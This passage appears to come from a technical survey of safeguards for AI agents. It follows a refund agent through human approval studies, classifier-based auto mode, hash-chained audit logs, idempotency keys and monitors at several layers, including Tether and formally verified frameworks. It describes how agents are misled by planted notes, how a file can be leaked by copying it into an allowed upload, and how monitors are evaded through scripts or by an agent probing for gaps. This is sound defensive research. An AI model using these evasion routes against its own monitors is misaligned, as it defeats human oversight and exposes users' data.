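Hossain and colleagues tested whether more informative prompts help. In one scenario, a user allows an agent to send only summary totals to an auditor. A planted note leads the agent to copy raw invoice rows into `report.csv`, and the agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The tool and the recipient are both permitted, so nothing in the request looks wrong.

Eighty volunteers each judged 12 requests, half of them unsafe, using one of four interfaces:

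| What the reviewer saw | Unsafe requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| Description and exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Arguments, user's restriction and full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, organised around the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from giving reviewers more facts. The last interface added a statement that the attachment came from raw invoice rows, with links to the evidence. Its advantage over the full log is uncertain, since the adjusted difference was 7.9 points, with a 95 percent interval from a 19.7-point improvement to a 3.8-point worsening. Even with the best interface, reviewers approved a quarter of unsafe requests. Half of the requests they saw were unsafe, and people would probably be less alert in ordinary use,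 where such requests are rare.

Good review also takes time. McCann's simulated refund agent escalated 112 requests while handling 200 refund cases. Reviewing those requests at 33 seconds each would take about an hour of concentrated work.

### Fewer prompts

If people run out of attention, the obvious remedy is to ask them less often. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) tested two ways of doing this with 113 people from outside the software industry. Each person supervised the same simulated day of 18 agent actions, seven of which went beyond the assigned task, such as buying an airport lounge pass or reading private messages.

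One group had to allow or deny every action. They spent 142 seconds, about eight per action, and blocked 60 percent of the actions that overreached. For a second group, a model had already cleared eight of the actions and left ten to the user, including all seven that overreached. This group blocked 54 percent. The third group first set standing rules of "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending, sending, deleting and reading private data. They saw 10.9 prompts on average but blocked only 40 percent.

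The standing rules failed mainly because people avoided making most decisions in advance. They chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, then approved two-thirds of the overreach when prompted. Some approvals may reflect real preferences, since nearly everyone allowed an unrequested call to the airport to confirm a flight. Yan also assigned some later recruits only to the standing-rules group, so assignment wasn't fully random. For the refund company, the result favours a fixed threshold that managers set over a rule that asks staff to decide every time.

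Another way to reduce prompts is to ask for approval of a whole plan. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) describes this in the research system ACE and in the coding agent Devin, which asks for approval of its plan and later of its finished code. Claude Code users rejected 39 percent of plans but only 3 percent of individual permission requests. This suggests people engage more with plans, though they may reject a plan because they dislike the approach rather than because it is dangerous. Plan approval also can't cover values the agent hasn't seen yet. A staff member could approve "refund the customer if the bicycle was damaged" before anyone knows the refund is 700 dollars, so the payment would still need its own check.

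### Automatic reviewers and waiting requests

Since August 2026, auto mode has been the default for new Claude Code sessions on Anthropic's individual and team plans. Its classifier reads the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the tools' output, so neither the agent's explanations nor text planted in the output can easily influence its decision. A quick check flags suspicious actions, and a slower one reviews them. If the classifier blocks three actions in a row or 20 in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user for approval.

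In the study with 1,053 testers, auto mode blocked 89 percent of the dangerous commands that the testers saw. In an earlier Anthropic test, the classifier missed 17 percent of 52 real cases in which Claude had exceeded what the user wanted. It wrongly blocked 0.4 percent of 10,000 ordinary calls. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised the danger but accepted weak evidence of consent. For example, a user might have asked Claude to "clean up the PR" without agreeing to overwrite shared history. Like an approval system that ignores arguments, the classifier treated consent to one action as consent to another.

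Anthropic says auto mode is an improvement for people who would otherwise skip permissions, but may be worse for anyone who reviews every action carefully. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves. The refund company can compare 700 with 500 without a classifier, but it could use one to pick out suspicious refunds below the limit and send those to staff as well.

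A runtime can also let work continue while a request waits, as KAIROS does when it defers an effect. This removes some of the pressure to answer quickly, though people still have just as many decisions to make. If each complaint has its own saved state, the refund agent can handle the next one while order 8042 waits, and a staff member can review all the waiting refunds on Monday morning. The staff member may then notice a pattern, such as several refunds to one card, but a long list also tempts people to approve everything at once. Stack Overflow's article proposes limiting how many requests an agent can send to people, for example to three an hour, after which the runtime suspends the agent until someone investigates. This prevents a faulty or hijacked agent from hiding one bad refund among a hundred harmless ones.

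## Recording and replaying decisions

Months after a refund, the company may have to show what its agent requested and why the system allowed or refused it. In ordinary software, the only evidence is the log lines the developers added, so an action without one is not recorded. A mediation point can record every request, including refused ones, before any effect happens, as McCann's runtime does.

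Refused requests can change how a reader interprets the rest of a log. *Auditable Agents* (2026) describes a record showing that an agent queried customer data and then emailed someone. The record omits that a policy check had blocked an earlier version of the email, and that the agent then rewrote it and got a person's approval. Two refunds of 320 dollars on one order look ordinary unless the log also shows a refused request for 640 dollars.

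Existing tools can fail to record the calls a model requests. In *Hearsay*, Dai, Yang and colleagues (2026) studied the records of several coding agents, including the widely used SWE-agent. When a model puts several tool calls in one reply, SWE-agent refuses the reply and asks for a single call, but saves neither the reply nor the refusal. In one set of 28 runs, 19 records lacked calls that the model had made.

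The agent's own summary is no substitute for a recorded log. *Plans They Abandon, Reports They Author* (2026) compared agents' reports with their action logs in 5,115 sessions and found that the reports mentioned 9.4 percent of the actions. Some of the omissions are due to brevity, since the median session had 59 actions and the median report contained four claims.

### Completeness, integrity and truth

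A log is complete if every request and effect has a record, so a script that pays a customer directly makes the log incomplete. A log has integrity if nobody has changed the records since the runtime wrote them. It loses that integrity if, for example, an employee changes 640 to 460 in an old record. A log is accurate about outcomes if the effects happened as it describes. Even a complete, unaltered log is inaccurate if it records a payment as made when the provider rejected it.

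McCann's ledger is complete as long as the runtime works as specified. McCann also writes that an auditor needs only the ledger, the policies and the hash function, and doesn't have to trust the runtime. With those three things, an auditor can recheck every recorded decision but can't detect a decision that the runtime never recorded.

Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Auditable Claims about AI Agents*, give a short proof of this limit. Suppose the company writes the only log. In one possible world, the agent made two refunds, both approved by a person. In another, it also made a third, unapproved refund that was never logged. The logs are identical, so any method that reads only the log must give the same verdict in both worlds. Confirming that a person approved every refund would be wrong in the second world, and denying it would be wrong in the first. Signing the log doesn't help, because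 the signatures are valid in both worlds.

The auditor therefore needs a record kept by someone else, such as the payment provider's statement. If the approval log is complete, a single payment without a matching entry disproves the company's claim. To confirm the claim, the auditor must match every payment. Zhao and colleagues constructed an example in which an agent's signed log lists three emails and passes verification, although the mail gateway recorded four.

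Dai and colleagues tested this on working software. They added a hash chain, a common protection against editing, to the log of the coding agent aider, and then made aider write false records as it ran. In 14 runs it left out a reply from the model, and in another 14 it added a sentence the model never produced. The chain passed verification in all 28 runs. They also examined the code of 16 agent frameworks, and none kept a record that an outsider could check without trusting the framework.

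A second ledger, kept outside the agent's control, recorded the agent's traffic with the model and the processes it started. Comparing the two accounts under rules fixed in advance exposed 64 of 66 alterations. The comparison raised no false alarms on 84 unaltered records, though in 15 of them it correctly identified calls that SWE-agent had dropped. Claude Sonnet 5, reading a different set of records without the ledger, detected only 49 percent of alterations.

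Even a second ledger can contain a false outcome. In another test, Dai and colleagues changed the output of a failing software test to a pass before it reached either the model or the log, so the ledger of model traffic also recorded a pass. The ledger separately recorded the test process's exit code, which revealed the failure in all 11 runs with a failure. For refunds, the equivalent is the provider's own record of what it paid.

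### A hash chain for three decisions

A hash function turns any data into a short value of fixed length, and in practice nobody can find other data that gives the same value. McCann's ledger links its records with one:

```
h_k = H(r_k || h_(k-1))
```

Here r_k is record number k, `||` joins two pieces of data, and h_0 is a fixed starting value. Each hash therefore depends on its own record and on all the earlier ones. The broken laptop produced three decisions, which form this chain (the hashes are invented and shortened, since real SHA-256 hashes have 64 characters):

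```

h0 = 0000
r1 = refund 640 on 7731, no approval, escalate  h1 = H(r1 || h0) = 4b1e
r2 = refund 640 on 7731, approved, allow        h2 = H(r2 || h1) = c07a
r3 = refund 640 on 7731, already paid, deny     h3 = H(r3 || h2) = 91d3
```

Suppose an employee changes the amount in r2 to 460. An auditor who recomputes the hash of r2 gets, say, 5f20 instead of c07a, so the edit is obvious. If the employee also replaces h2 with 5f20, h3 no longer matches, because it was computed from c07a.

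But H is public and needs no secret key. An employee who can write to the whole table can recompute h3 as well, and the altered chain is then as consistent as the original. Deleting r3 is even easier, because r1 and r2 form a valid chain that ends at c07a. An auditor can detect these changes only with a copy of 91d3 from somewhere the employee couldn't reach:

| What happened | Does the chain alone reveal it? | Does a saved copy of h3 reveal it? |
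|---|---|---|
| Someone edited r2 | Yes | Yes |
| Someone edited r2 and recomputed h2 and h3 | No | Yes |
| Someone deleted r3 and h3 | No | Yes |
| The runtime never recorded a fourth request | No | No |

*aiAuthZ* (2026) describes an authorisation service for agents. The service has a function that returns the latest hash so that operators can save it elsewhere, for example in storage that blocks changes and deletions. The saved hash protects only the records that came before it, so if operators save one every midnight, an intruder at noon can rewrite all of that morning's records.

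A chain also makes customers' data harder to delete, because removing an old record breaks every later link. *aiAuthZ* encrypts the sensitive content, stores it separately, and puts only its hash in the chain. The service can then erase the content without removing the decision from the log or invalidating the chain.

### Logs that outsiders can check

If the company itself is under suspicion, the saved hash has to be outside its control. *A Black Box for Agentic Processes* (2026) makes the general point that an auditor still has to trust the operator if the operator runs the append-only log.

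Certificate Transparency addresses the same problem on the web. Browsers rely on certificates to confirm that they have reached the real site, so an authority that issues one to the wrong party lets that party impersonate the site. Site owners can check public logs of certificates for any they didn't expect. *RFC 9162*, by Laurie, Messeri and Stradling, specifies the current version.

These logs use a *Merkle tree* instead of a simple chain. The log hashes each record, then hashes the results in pairs, and repeats this until a single hash, the root, remains. Anyone can check that a record is in a log of a million entries by recomputing the root from that record and about 20 other hashes supplied by the log. With a simple chain, they would need every later record. A similar short proof shows that today's log begins with all of yesterday's log, unchanged.

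The mathematics still doesn't guarantee that the log is complete. Laurie and colleagues propose that browsers eventually reject certificates that aren't in a log, which would force authorities to submit them. The refund company could get a similar guarantee if its payment provider rejected refunds that came without proof of a log entry, including any requested by a script that contacted the provider directly.

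One weakness of Certificate Transparency is that a dishonest log operator can show different people different versions of the log. Laurie and colleagues therefore treat each log as a trusted third party and leave solving the problem to other work.

Bindschaedler, Botha and Siebenbrunner (2026), in *Agent Flight Recorder*, publish the root of each batch of agent records on a public blockchain. With 100 records per batch, this costs $2.30 per 100,000 records. They consider it worthwhile mainly when two organisations are in dispute and never agreed on a neutral party. For internal audits, they recommend a hash chain in write-once storage. Partners with an agreed auditor may find a transparency log or a timestamping service cheaper and simpler. They explicitly don't promise a complete record, because the recorder protects only the events that reach it.

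### A crash between the record and the payment

Suppose the server crashes after the runtime has recorded "allowed" for the 640-dollar refund but before it has recorded an outcome. The ledger is the same whether the request was never sent or the provider has already paid. If the runtime tries again after restarting, it may pay the customer twice, and if it gives up, the customer may get nothing. The same problem occurs without a crash if the provider's confirmation is lost.

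Before retrying a payment, a system can ask the provider whether it has paid, but this check can miss a request that is still on its way. Li (2026), in *Where Does Exactly-Once Live?*, tested the check in 25,930 trials with simulated services, nine models and several kinds of fault. When the service had acted and only its reply was lost, leading models almost always checked before retrying, and duplicated the action in 0.5 percent of trials. When the request was still on its way, they duplicated the action in 56 percent of trials, because they checked, found nothing and sent the request again, and then both requests took effect.

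Li proves that no amount of checking can solve this unless there is a known limit on how long a request can stay in transit. Suppose a refund request times out. It may be lost, or it may be delayed and take effect in two hours. Until then, every check gives the same answer in both cases. An agent that resends a lost request within an hour will therefore also resend a delayed one, and the customer will be refunded twice. In Li's tests with widely varying delays, waiting an hour before checking still led to duplicates in 16 percent of trials.

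An *idempotency key* removes the need to know what happened. It is an identifier that the client attaches to a request. The service acts on each key at most once, and if the key arrives again, it returns the original result. The runtime can store the key in the ledger record before it sends anything:

```
write(request, "allow", key = "refund-7731-a")
result = provider.pay(request, key = "refund-7731-a")
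write("refund-7731-a", result)

after a restart:
    for each allowed request without a result:
        result = provider.pay(request, its stored key)
        write(its stored key, result)
```

If the provider never received the refund request, it pays now. If it has already paid, it returns the original receipt. Either way, the customer receives 640 dollars once, and the system records the missing outcome in the ledger.

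In Li's tests, adding a key option to every action that needed one cut duplicates from 28 to 4 percent. The remaining duplicates came from agents that sent the first attempt without a key or invented a new one for the retry. None of the 432 retries of delayed requests that reused the original key caused a duplicate. The runtime should therefore choose the key, and use one per intended refund, so that two separate 100-dollar refunds don't count as one. Zihao Wang (2026), in *Callability Is Not Operability*, found that interfaces with protections of this kind reduced duplicates by 56.9 percentage points when replies went missing after an action.

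Keys work only if the service supports them. In Li's simulation, which followed the conventions of real services, only two of the 11 kinds of action that needed a key accepted one. Without a key, the safest course is to record the outcome as unknown and ask a person. Automatic retries are especially risky. When Li added a layer that silently resent failed requests, the share of trials in which every action happened exactly once fell from 72 to 50 percent. The agents described the task as completed in 90 percent of the trials with a duplicate, so their reports wouldn't have revealed the damage.

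### What recording costs

McCann measured how much time the checkpoint adds to each request, over 10,000 repetitions on a laptop-class processor. The median was 535 microseconds, and the checkpoint added more than 1,200 microseconds to one request in a hundred. Checking 20 policy rules took about one microsecond and computing the hash took less, so writing to the database took nearly all of the time.

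This overhead is less than 5 percent of an operation's time only if the operation takes longer than 10.7 milliseconds. McCann describes it as less than 5 percent and gives database queries of 1 to 50 milliseconds as an example, which is wrong for the faster queries. The overhead is about 54 percent of a 1-millisecond query and 1 percent of a 50-millisecond one. It is negligible for an agent that waits seconds for each model reply, but it might noticeably slow a program that makes thousands of quick queries.

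The figure also depends on a setting that makes the ledger less durable. McCann used the database SQLite in a mode that appends changes to a separate file, with the option `synchronous=NORMAL`. According to SQLite's documentation, this option doesn't force each change onto the disk, so a power failure can undo recent ones. A crash of the program alone doesn't undo them, as SQLite's developers explain in a passage quoted in *Process vs OS level durability (sync=NORMAL, WAL)* (2020), a thread on the SQLite forum.

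If the power fails just after the provider pays, the record of the payment may therefore be lost, along with its idempotency key, even though the runtime wrote the record before the payment. The hash chain does not reveal the loss, because the missing records come from the end and the shorter chain is still valid. The stricter setting, `FULL`, forces every change to disk before the program continues. A payment ledger needs this setting, though McCann gives no timings for it.

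### Replaying old requests under a new policy

The ledger also lets the company test a new policy on old requests. For each recorded request i_k and its context c_k, the runtime computes the decision under the new policy P′:

```
new decision k = decide(P′, i_k, c_k)
```

Replaying recorded decisions under new rules runs no agent and causes no effects. It works only if the decision function always gives the same answer for the same inputs and the record contains all the context the new rules need. For example, a rule based on a fraud score can't be tested on records without fraud scores.

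McCann replayed the 847 requests from the simulated refund workload with the refund limit raised from 500 to 1,000 dollars. Of the 312 refusals, 89 became approvals. McCann concludes that the higher limit would speed up medium-sized refunds, but the replay shows only that 89 decisions would change. The laptop's three records illustrate the difference:

| Recorded request | Original decision | Decision with a 1,000-dollar limit |
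|---|---|---|
| 640 dollars, no approval | Escalate | Allow |
| 640 dollars, approved | Allow | Allow |
| 640 dollars, already refunded | Deny | Deny |

The replay allows two refunds totaling 1,280 dollars. The rule against double refunds doesn't catch the second one, because the context recorded with that request shows no earlier payment. In reality, the company would have paid the first request at once, and nobody would have submitted it again with an approval. The 89 changed decisions could likewise include several attempts at the same refund.

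In each run, a replay is reliable up to the first decision that changes. Later records describe how the agent responded to an answer it would no longer have received. If a stricter policy refuses a refund that the old one allowed, the ledger still contains the email telling the customer that the money is on its way. It can't show whether the agent would have apologised, asked a colleague or split the refund into smaller ones. *Causal Attribution for Agentic Decisions* (2026) notes more generally that a step can matter mainly because it changes the choice made at a later step, and finds no monitoring tool that records enough to measure this.

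Replay is better suited to judging past actions by a new standard, where the agent's next move doesn't matter. *CAREFUL-BENCH* (Kovalenko and Redchych, 2026) re-executed logged tool calls in a benchmark's simulated services without rerunning the models. The original benchmark compared only the final state with the expected one, so it didn't penalise extra calls along the way. The replay could count duplicate writes and unrequested deletions.

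To find out what an agent would have done, someone has to run it again. *Attributing Agent Failures to Their History Needs an Executed Counterfactual* (2026) describes restoring a saved state, changing what the agent has been told, and letting it continue. The agent's environment has to match what it is told. If the agent reads that its refund went through while the order database shows no refund, the situation could never have occurred. The company would therefore restart from just before the changed decision, with a simulated payment provider (much like a dry-run handler) that updates a copy of the order. It would also need many runs, because a model may act differently in the same situation. In Li's tests, two runs of the same situation took the same first step after a timeout only 82 percent of the time.

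## Which effects the checkpoint really covers

An approval rule, a refund limit and a ledger apply only to effects that reach the checkpoint. Developers can put the checkpoint in the programming language, in the framework's tool dispatcher (the code that matches each tool call to a function and runs it), or at the edge of the operating system or virtual machine around the agent. A checkpoint in the language has the most information about what each action means, but the fewest actions bypass one at the edge of the machine.

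### One refund at three layers

Suppose the agent writes a script that refunds $640 on order 7731. In a language like McCann's, the script can reach the payment provider only through a request, so the checkpoint receives the operation, the order and the amount as separate fields.

A tool dispatcher receives the same information if the script calls `issue_refund`. But an agent with a shell tool can save a script that contacts the provider directly, then request the command `python refund.py`. The dispatcher receives that command as a single string, which contains neither the operation nor the amount.

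At the machine boundary, both scripts produce a normally encrypted connection to the provider. KAIROS decrypts this traffic at a proxy whose certificate authority is built into the virtual machine, so its monitor receives a readable web request. But some payment services count in cents, so a 640-dollar payment might appear as 64000. Whoever writes the 500-dollar rule at this layer has to know the provider's message format.

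| Layer | Script that calls `issue_refund` | Script that contacts the provider directly |
|---|---|---|
| Language | Refund, order 7731, 640 dollars | Programs cannot express this |
| Tool dispatcher | Tool name and arguments | The command `python refund.py` |
| Machine boundary | Web request to the provider, usually encrypted | Web request to the provider, usually encrypted |

The entry "Programs cannot express this" is true only if the language gives programs no way to run outside software. TACIT's type checks, for instance, don't cover external programs, and Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that the guarantee is then only as good as the list of permitted commands. They recommend a short list of specific safe commands, such as `git diff` and `sbt`, plus a sandbox where security is critical. Even a short list can permit a lot, because `sbt` is a build tool that runs code from the project's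 build file, which a coding agent may have permission to edit.

### The case for the machine boundary

Hempel and colleagues put KAIROS at the edge of a virtual machine because a dispatcher covers only declared tools, and whether those account for every effect depends on how each agent is set up. The virtual machine has a small, fixed set of channels to the outside, however the agent acts. A checkpoint in the framework also requires modifying the framework, which excludes closed-source agents, and its guarantee has to be re-established whenever the agent changes.

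The drawback of checking at the machine boundary is a "semantic gap". A rule about tools can refer to an operation and to the role of each argument, such as the recipient of a payment. A rule at the machine boundary can refer only to a path or destination and the values sent there, so some rules that are possible for tools can't be written. KAIROS has to pass the remaining cases to its judge. Its benchmark results don't show how large an effect this has, because the adapter for the simulated tools supplied their names and arguments. The policy also specified which tools were reversible and which argument named the destination, details that file operations and web requests don't include.

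The KAIROS proxy exempts one channel from checking, the agent's traffic to its model provider. The agent has to reach its language model, so the proxy logs this traffic and lets it through, assuming that the provider does not collude with the attacker. Even an honest provider may offer a service through which data can leave. Odersky and colleagues cite a case in which a researcher extracted user data through Anthropic's Files API.

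### The same rule for typed tools and a shell

Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, show how much a rule loses when actions arrive as shell commands. In their example, an agent may upload status reports to an outside site but must not upload `servers.csv`, the company's confidential inventory. It takes three steps:

```
(1) upload report.txt
(2) copy servers.csv to report.txt
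(3) upload report.txt
```

Steps 1 and 3 use the same command, but by step 3 the report contains the inventory. A checkpoint has to allow the command in step 1 and refuse it in step 3.

Sistla and colleagues first write the rule in Dogwood, an Amazon policy language whose rules can refer to earlier events. With typed file tools, a copy event has separate fields for its source and destination, so the rule can forbid uploading a file that the agent copied from `servers.csv` and has not rewritten since. With a generic shell tool, each event is a command string, and Dogwood can match an earlier command only by its exact text. The rule therefore does not detect the same copy made with a differently written command.

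Typed tools help less when the agent copies the inventory to a temporary file and then copies that file to the report. The rule doesn't apply because the report's immediate source is the temporary file. More rules can cover longer chains of copies, but each chain of j copies has mʲ possible forms if m tools can copy files. Covering every chain of up to k copies therefore takes m + m² + … + mᵏ patterns, which is 120 for three tools and up to four copies. A ban on uploading anything written after the agent read the inventory would catch every chain, but it would also block harmless files.

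### How Tether recovers the meaning of a command

Sistla and colleagues' own system, Tether, attaches a confidentiality label to each file instead of searching the history. It handles a shell command in four steps:

1. Tether runs the command on a disposable copy-on-write layer over the file system. A tracer records the command's system calls, which are its requests to the operating system.
2. Tether translates the system calls into 11 kinds of abstract action, such as read, copy and upload. If a process reads one file and then writes another, Tether counts this as a copy.
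3. A monitor checks each action against the policy and updates the labels. A proxy holds each outgoing request until the monitor has allowed everything the command has done so far.
4. If the monitor allows every action, Tether applies the file changes to the real system. Otherwise it discards them.

In simplified form, the example needs only these rules:

```
copy(s, d):        label(d) becomes label(s)
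upload(s, host):   allow only if label(s) is Public
```

Step 2 of the example labels the report "Sensitive", so the monitor blocks step 3. Each copy gets the label of its source file, so the rule works for a chain of any length, and copies of public files stay public.

System calls don't show whether the data a process wrote depended on the data it read, so Tether assumes that it did. This avoids missed leaks but causes false alarms. For example, when an agent searches a whole directory for a word, the search opens every file, including secret ones, and Tether treats the agent as having read them.

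Tether recovers which file went where, but not the details of a payment, such as its amount. Its rules compare labels and check whether a file or host is on a list, so they can restrict which programs' data reaches the payment provider but can't express a 500-dollar limit on payments.

### What the Tether tests show

Sistla and colleagues replayed recorded agent runs from two benchmarks of programming and system administration, some with a harmful side task. They ran an open-source version of Claude Code's auto mode on the same runs, both with its default rules and with Tether's policy written into them:

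| Monitor | Harmful runs blocked, out of 344 | Harmless runs blocked, out of 1,590 |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 100% | 4.7% |
| Auto mode, default rules | 91.6% | 9.7% |
| Auto mode, Tether's policy | 89.2% | 3.5% |

Auto mode missed attacks inside scripts because the command line didn't show what the scripts would do. The dispatcher has the same problem with `python refund.py`. Even a better classifier would need to read the script or monitor it as it runs.

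Tether's perfect score covers only the runs that Sistla and colleagues kept, those in which Tether could trace and interpret every action. Their selection left out runs with background processes or database queries, and attacks that break no rule about where data goes, such as malicious code in a file the agent may edit. They report that 28.2 percent of runs on one benchmark and 22.1 percent on the other require a judgment about content, which no monitor of this kind can make. They also refined the policy by testing it on benchmark runs, so it may do worse on unfamiliar tasks.

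Tether's labels depend on translating system calls correctly. To test this, Sistla and colleagues generated random chains of file operations, ran each one through different system mechanisms, and compared the resulting decisions and labels with the correct ones. They also told an AI agent to get around the monitor on ten tasks. Its success rate fell from 40 percent to zero over three versions of Tether as they fixed the gaps the agent exposed. One gap concerned hard links, which give a file a second name. Ten tasks can't establish that no gaps remain.

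### Tools that do more than their descriptions say

A dispatcher's rules depend on someone classifying each tool correctly. Kovalenko and Redchych examined the 128 functions in the multi-turn part of the Berkeley Function Calling Leaderboard, a widely used benchmark. The descriptions given to the model contain no indication that a call deletes something, sends something or makes a payment.

Each function was classified by running it in the benchmark's simulated services and comparing the state before and after. This gave 79 reads and 49 writes. Some results differed from what the documentation suggested. Cancelling an order a second time fails without changing anything further, whereas repeating a file copy can change the state again. A runtime that retries failed calls must account for this difference.

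This method requires a simulator or a test account and covers only the inputs someone tries. One function returned an error in all 82 calls and counted as a read because it never changed anything. Deciding which writes are destructive also takes judgment. Two people and two language models labelled the functions and agreed on 38 of the 49 writes. They split evenly on whether overwriting a file's content counts as deletion.

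The Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting agents to tools, lets developers label a tool as read-only, destructive or idempotent. The specification treats these labels as advisory. When Kovalenko and Redchych added such labels to the function descriptions, the behaviour of the eight models they tested did not measurably change. A checkpoint could enforce rules based on the labels, but a careless or malicious developer could still mark a deletion as read-only.

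Suppose the refund company's `read_order` tool also sends customer details to an advertising firm. A dispatcher would treat the call as a read and allow it. If the tool runs inside the agent's virtual machine, a monitor at the machine's boundary would receive the connection to the advertising firm as a separate event. If the tool runs on an outside server, both checkpoints would receive only the query to that server.

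### Other routes to an effect

A background process or scheduled job can avoid a checkpoint by acting after the command that created it has finished. Tether's tracer stops when the main command ends, so its policy has to forbid such processes or refer them to a person. A checkpoint can also miss effects that occur inside software whose internal workings the monitor doesn't model. For example, a single query can make a database copy private data from one table to another, and a monitor that tracks only files can't follow the copy.

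A program in a restricted language may also load components written in an unrestricted one. TACIT's guarantee does not cover timing leaks, in which an agent reveals one bit of a secret by varying how long it takes to process it. KAIROS does not cover such covert channels either, or any harm done by the text of the agent's reply to its user.

The safe default is to close any route a monitor can't interpret. Sistla and colleagues estimate that blocking background processes and database access would let Tether intercept a further 36.3 percent of runs on one benchmark and 71.5 percent on the other. These figures don't separate harmful runs from harmless ones. On a server where most work involves a database, blocking database access would probably stop the agent from doing its job.

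### A model that may request anything

Tests cover the actions that someone thought to try. Moon and Varshney (2026), in *Containment Verification*, instead prove that a framework enforces its policy for every action the model could request. They write the framework's core in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in proof checker, and represent the model as a function with no body:

```dafny
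method {:extern} GetActionFromLLM(c: Constants, v: Variables)
    returns (action: Action)
```

The declaration gives Dafny only the result's type, `Action`, which lists the operations the framework offers. Any proof about the surrounding code must therefore hold for every possible sequence of actions. Such a proof applies however hostile or capable the model is.

The proof compares two state machines. One is a simple specification that always obeys the policy, and the other describes how the framework operates. At each step, a machine in state s receives an action a, emits an event e and moves to state s′. If the machine refuses the action, e is a "no effect" event. The policy is a condition Π(s, a, e, s′) that every step must satisfy. Moon and Varshney show that the framework *refines* the specification, which requires three things:

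1. The two machines start in matching states.
2. From matching states, whenever the framework can take a step, the specification can take one for the same action. The two steps emit matching events and end in matching states.
3. If the specification's step obeys the policy, so does the framework's.

For any run of the framework, these conditions make it possible to construct a matching run of the specification, one step at a time. Every step of the specification's run obeys the policy, so every step of the framework's run does too.

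Suppose the refund agent's specification requires "no effect" for an unapproved request for 640 dollars, but a typo sets the framework's limit at 5,000 dollars. The framework would emit a payment, but no step in the specification has a matching event. The second condition fails, so Dafny rejects the proof before anyone runs the agent.

### The PocketFlow proof and its assumption

Moon and Varshney applied the method to PocketFlow, a minimal framework for building agents. They proved that an agent can read files only inside its workspace, call only tools on an approved list, and take only a limited number of steps. Dafny then translated the verified code into Python.

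Proving these rules for the refund agent would show that it can call `issue_refund` only if that tool is on the list. The proof would not cover the 500-dollar limit unless someone added the limit to the policy. If the list included a shell, the guarantee would be nearly worthless, because every shell command would count as a permitted tool call. Moon and Varshney acknowledge that a generic shell "collapses the guarantee onto the primitive".

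Language models wrote the specifications and proofs. The model that wrote the safety properties had no access to the code, because it might otherwise have produced a specification that merely restated the code, making the proof pointless. The process also deliberately damaged each proof and rejected the specification if Dafny still accepted the result.

These precautions did not catch every empty specification. In a comparison run, Moon and Varshney let the model read the code of a document-retrieval agent whose operations did not fit the template for safety properties. The model left one of the template's fields unused. The rule about that field was true in every run because it had nothing to restrict, and Dafny accepted the proof. The refund company would make an equivalent mistake if it proved that every payment in a list is under 500 dollars when no code ever adds a payment to the list.

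The guarantee also depends on *effect exclusivity*, the assumption that every external effect available to the agent passes through the typed interface. The proof does not establish this assumption, which is the same as complete mediation. The verified code runs as Python, where any other code in the process could call the network library directly. Moon and Varshney therefore recommend adding a sandbox, restricting the process's permissions, and reviewing the code that connects the model to the verified part.

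### McCann's wrapper around a handler

McCann uses Rocq, a proof assistant, to prove properties of a checkpoint that wraps an effect handler. In outline, the wrapper G turns any handler h into a checked one:

```
G(h)(request):
    run four checks
    if all pass:   result = h(request)
                   run three follow-up steps
                   return result
    otherwise:     loop forever
```

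The checks cover trust, permissions, the current phase and any preliminary hooks. The follow-up steps apply guardrails, record the event and announce it. Because the guardrails run after the effect, they cannot prevent it. A refused request never reaches the recording step, whereas in McCann's calculus every refusal adds a record to the ledger.

The *safety theorem* covers every handler and every program, including programs that run forever. It guarantees that the wrapped program performs input or output only while a flag is true. The flag starts as false and becomes true when a check occurs. This guarantee is weaker than it sounds because McCann's flag becomes true whether the check passes or fails, and it never returns to false, so a program could fail one check, issue a thousand refunds, and still satisfy the definition.

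G itself rules out such a program, because it checks each request separately and never calls h after a failed check. A separate theorem about a model of the runtime's decisions proves that a denied request causes no input or output. Anyone relying on the work should cite that theorem and the definition of G along with the safety theorem.

The *transparency theorem* shows that when every check passes, the wrapped program performs the same input and output in the same order as the original and returns the same result. For example, if a 40-dollar refund passes the checks, the customer still gets 40 dollars and the same email. The theorem doesn't cover timing, so a slow check could still make a payment late. It also doesn't apply to runs with a refusal.

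In those runs, the wrapped program never returns after a refusal. It can't produce a wrong result, but the refund agent also can't send the email "A colleague will contact you." A runtime that returns `denied` to the program, as in McCann's calculus, follows different rules from G, so it needs its own proof.

### 454 theorems and 70,000 tests

McCann's Rocq development contains 454 theorems in about 12,000 lines, with no unproved steps. The work is smaller than that count suggests, since McCann classes 30 of the theorems as core results and 102 as supporting lemmas, and many of the others confirm that a definition covers every kind of request.

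These theorems concern a mathematical model. To check the working software against it, McCann wrote a 148-line reference interpreter that follows the Rocq specification, then compared its decisions with the runtime's on random requests. The tests covered seven properties with 10,000 inputs each. On the 188th input, the specification allowed a shell command that the runtime refused, because the required permission was missing from the runtime's permission tree. The unit tests had missed this fault, which made the runtime too strict. After McCann fixed it, more than 70,000 tests produced no disagreement.

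McCann is inconsistent about what the tests covered. The method description refers to the deployed runtime, but the list of limitations refers to a reference interpreter and not the runtime directly. Random testing can also miss rare faults. If a fault affects one in 10,000 generated inputs, a set of 10,000 tests has a 37 percent chance of missing it.

The tests also compare decisions about requests, so they can't detect an effect that never became a request. Testing for complete mediation would require recording the machine's network traffic and file changes from outside and looking for any without a matching ledger entry.

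### What each guarantee trusts

The trusted computing bases differ mainly in how much ordinary software they include:

| System | Parts that must work correctly |
|---|---|
| TACIT | Scala compiler with its safety checks, TACIT's library, the runtime, and the separate model that reads secret data, if the developers use one |
| KAIROS | Isolation layer, host computer and monitor |
| Tether | Host kernel, system-call tracer, file-system layer, network proxy, translation into abstract actions, and Lean (the language of its monitor and proofs) with its compiler and runtime |
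| Verified PocketFlow | Policy, the mapping between specification and framework, Dafny's verifier and compiler, the code that turns model output into typed actions, and the barrier against other effects |
| McCann's wrapper | Rocq's proof checker, two proof libraries, and a runtime that follows the model and has no hidden effects |

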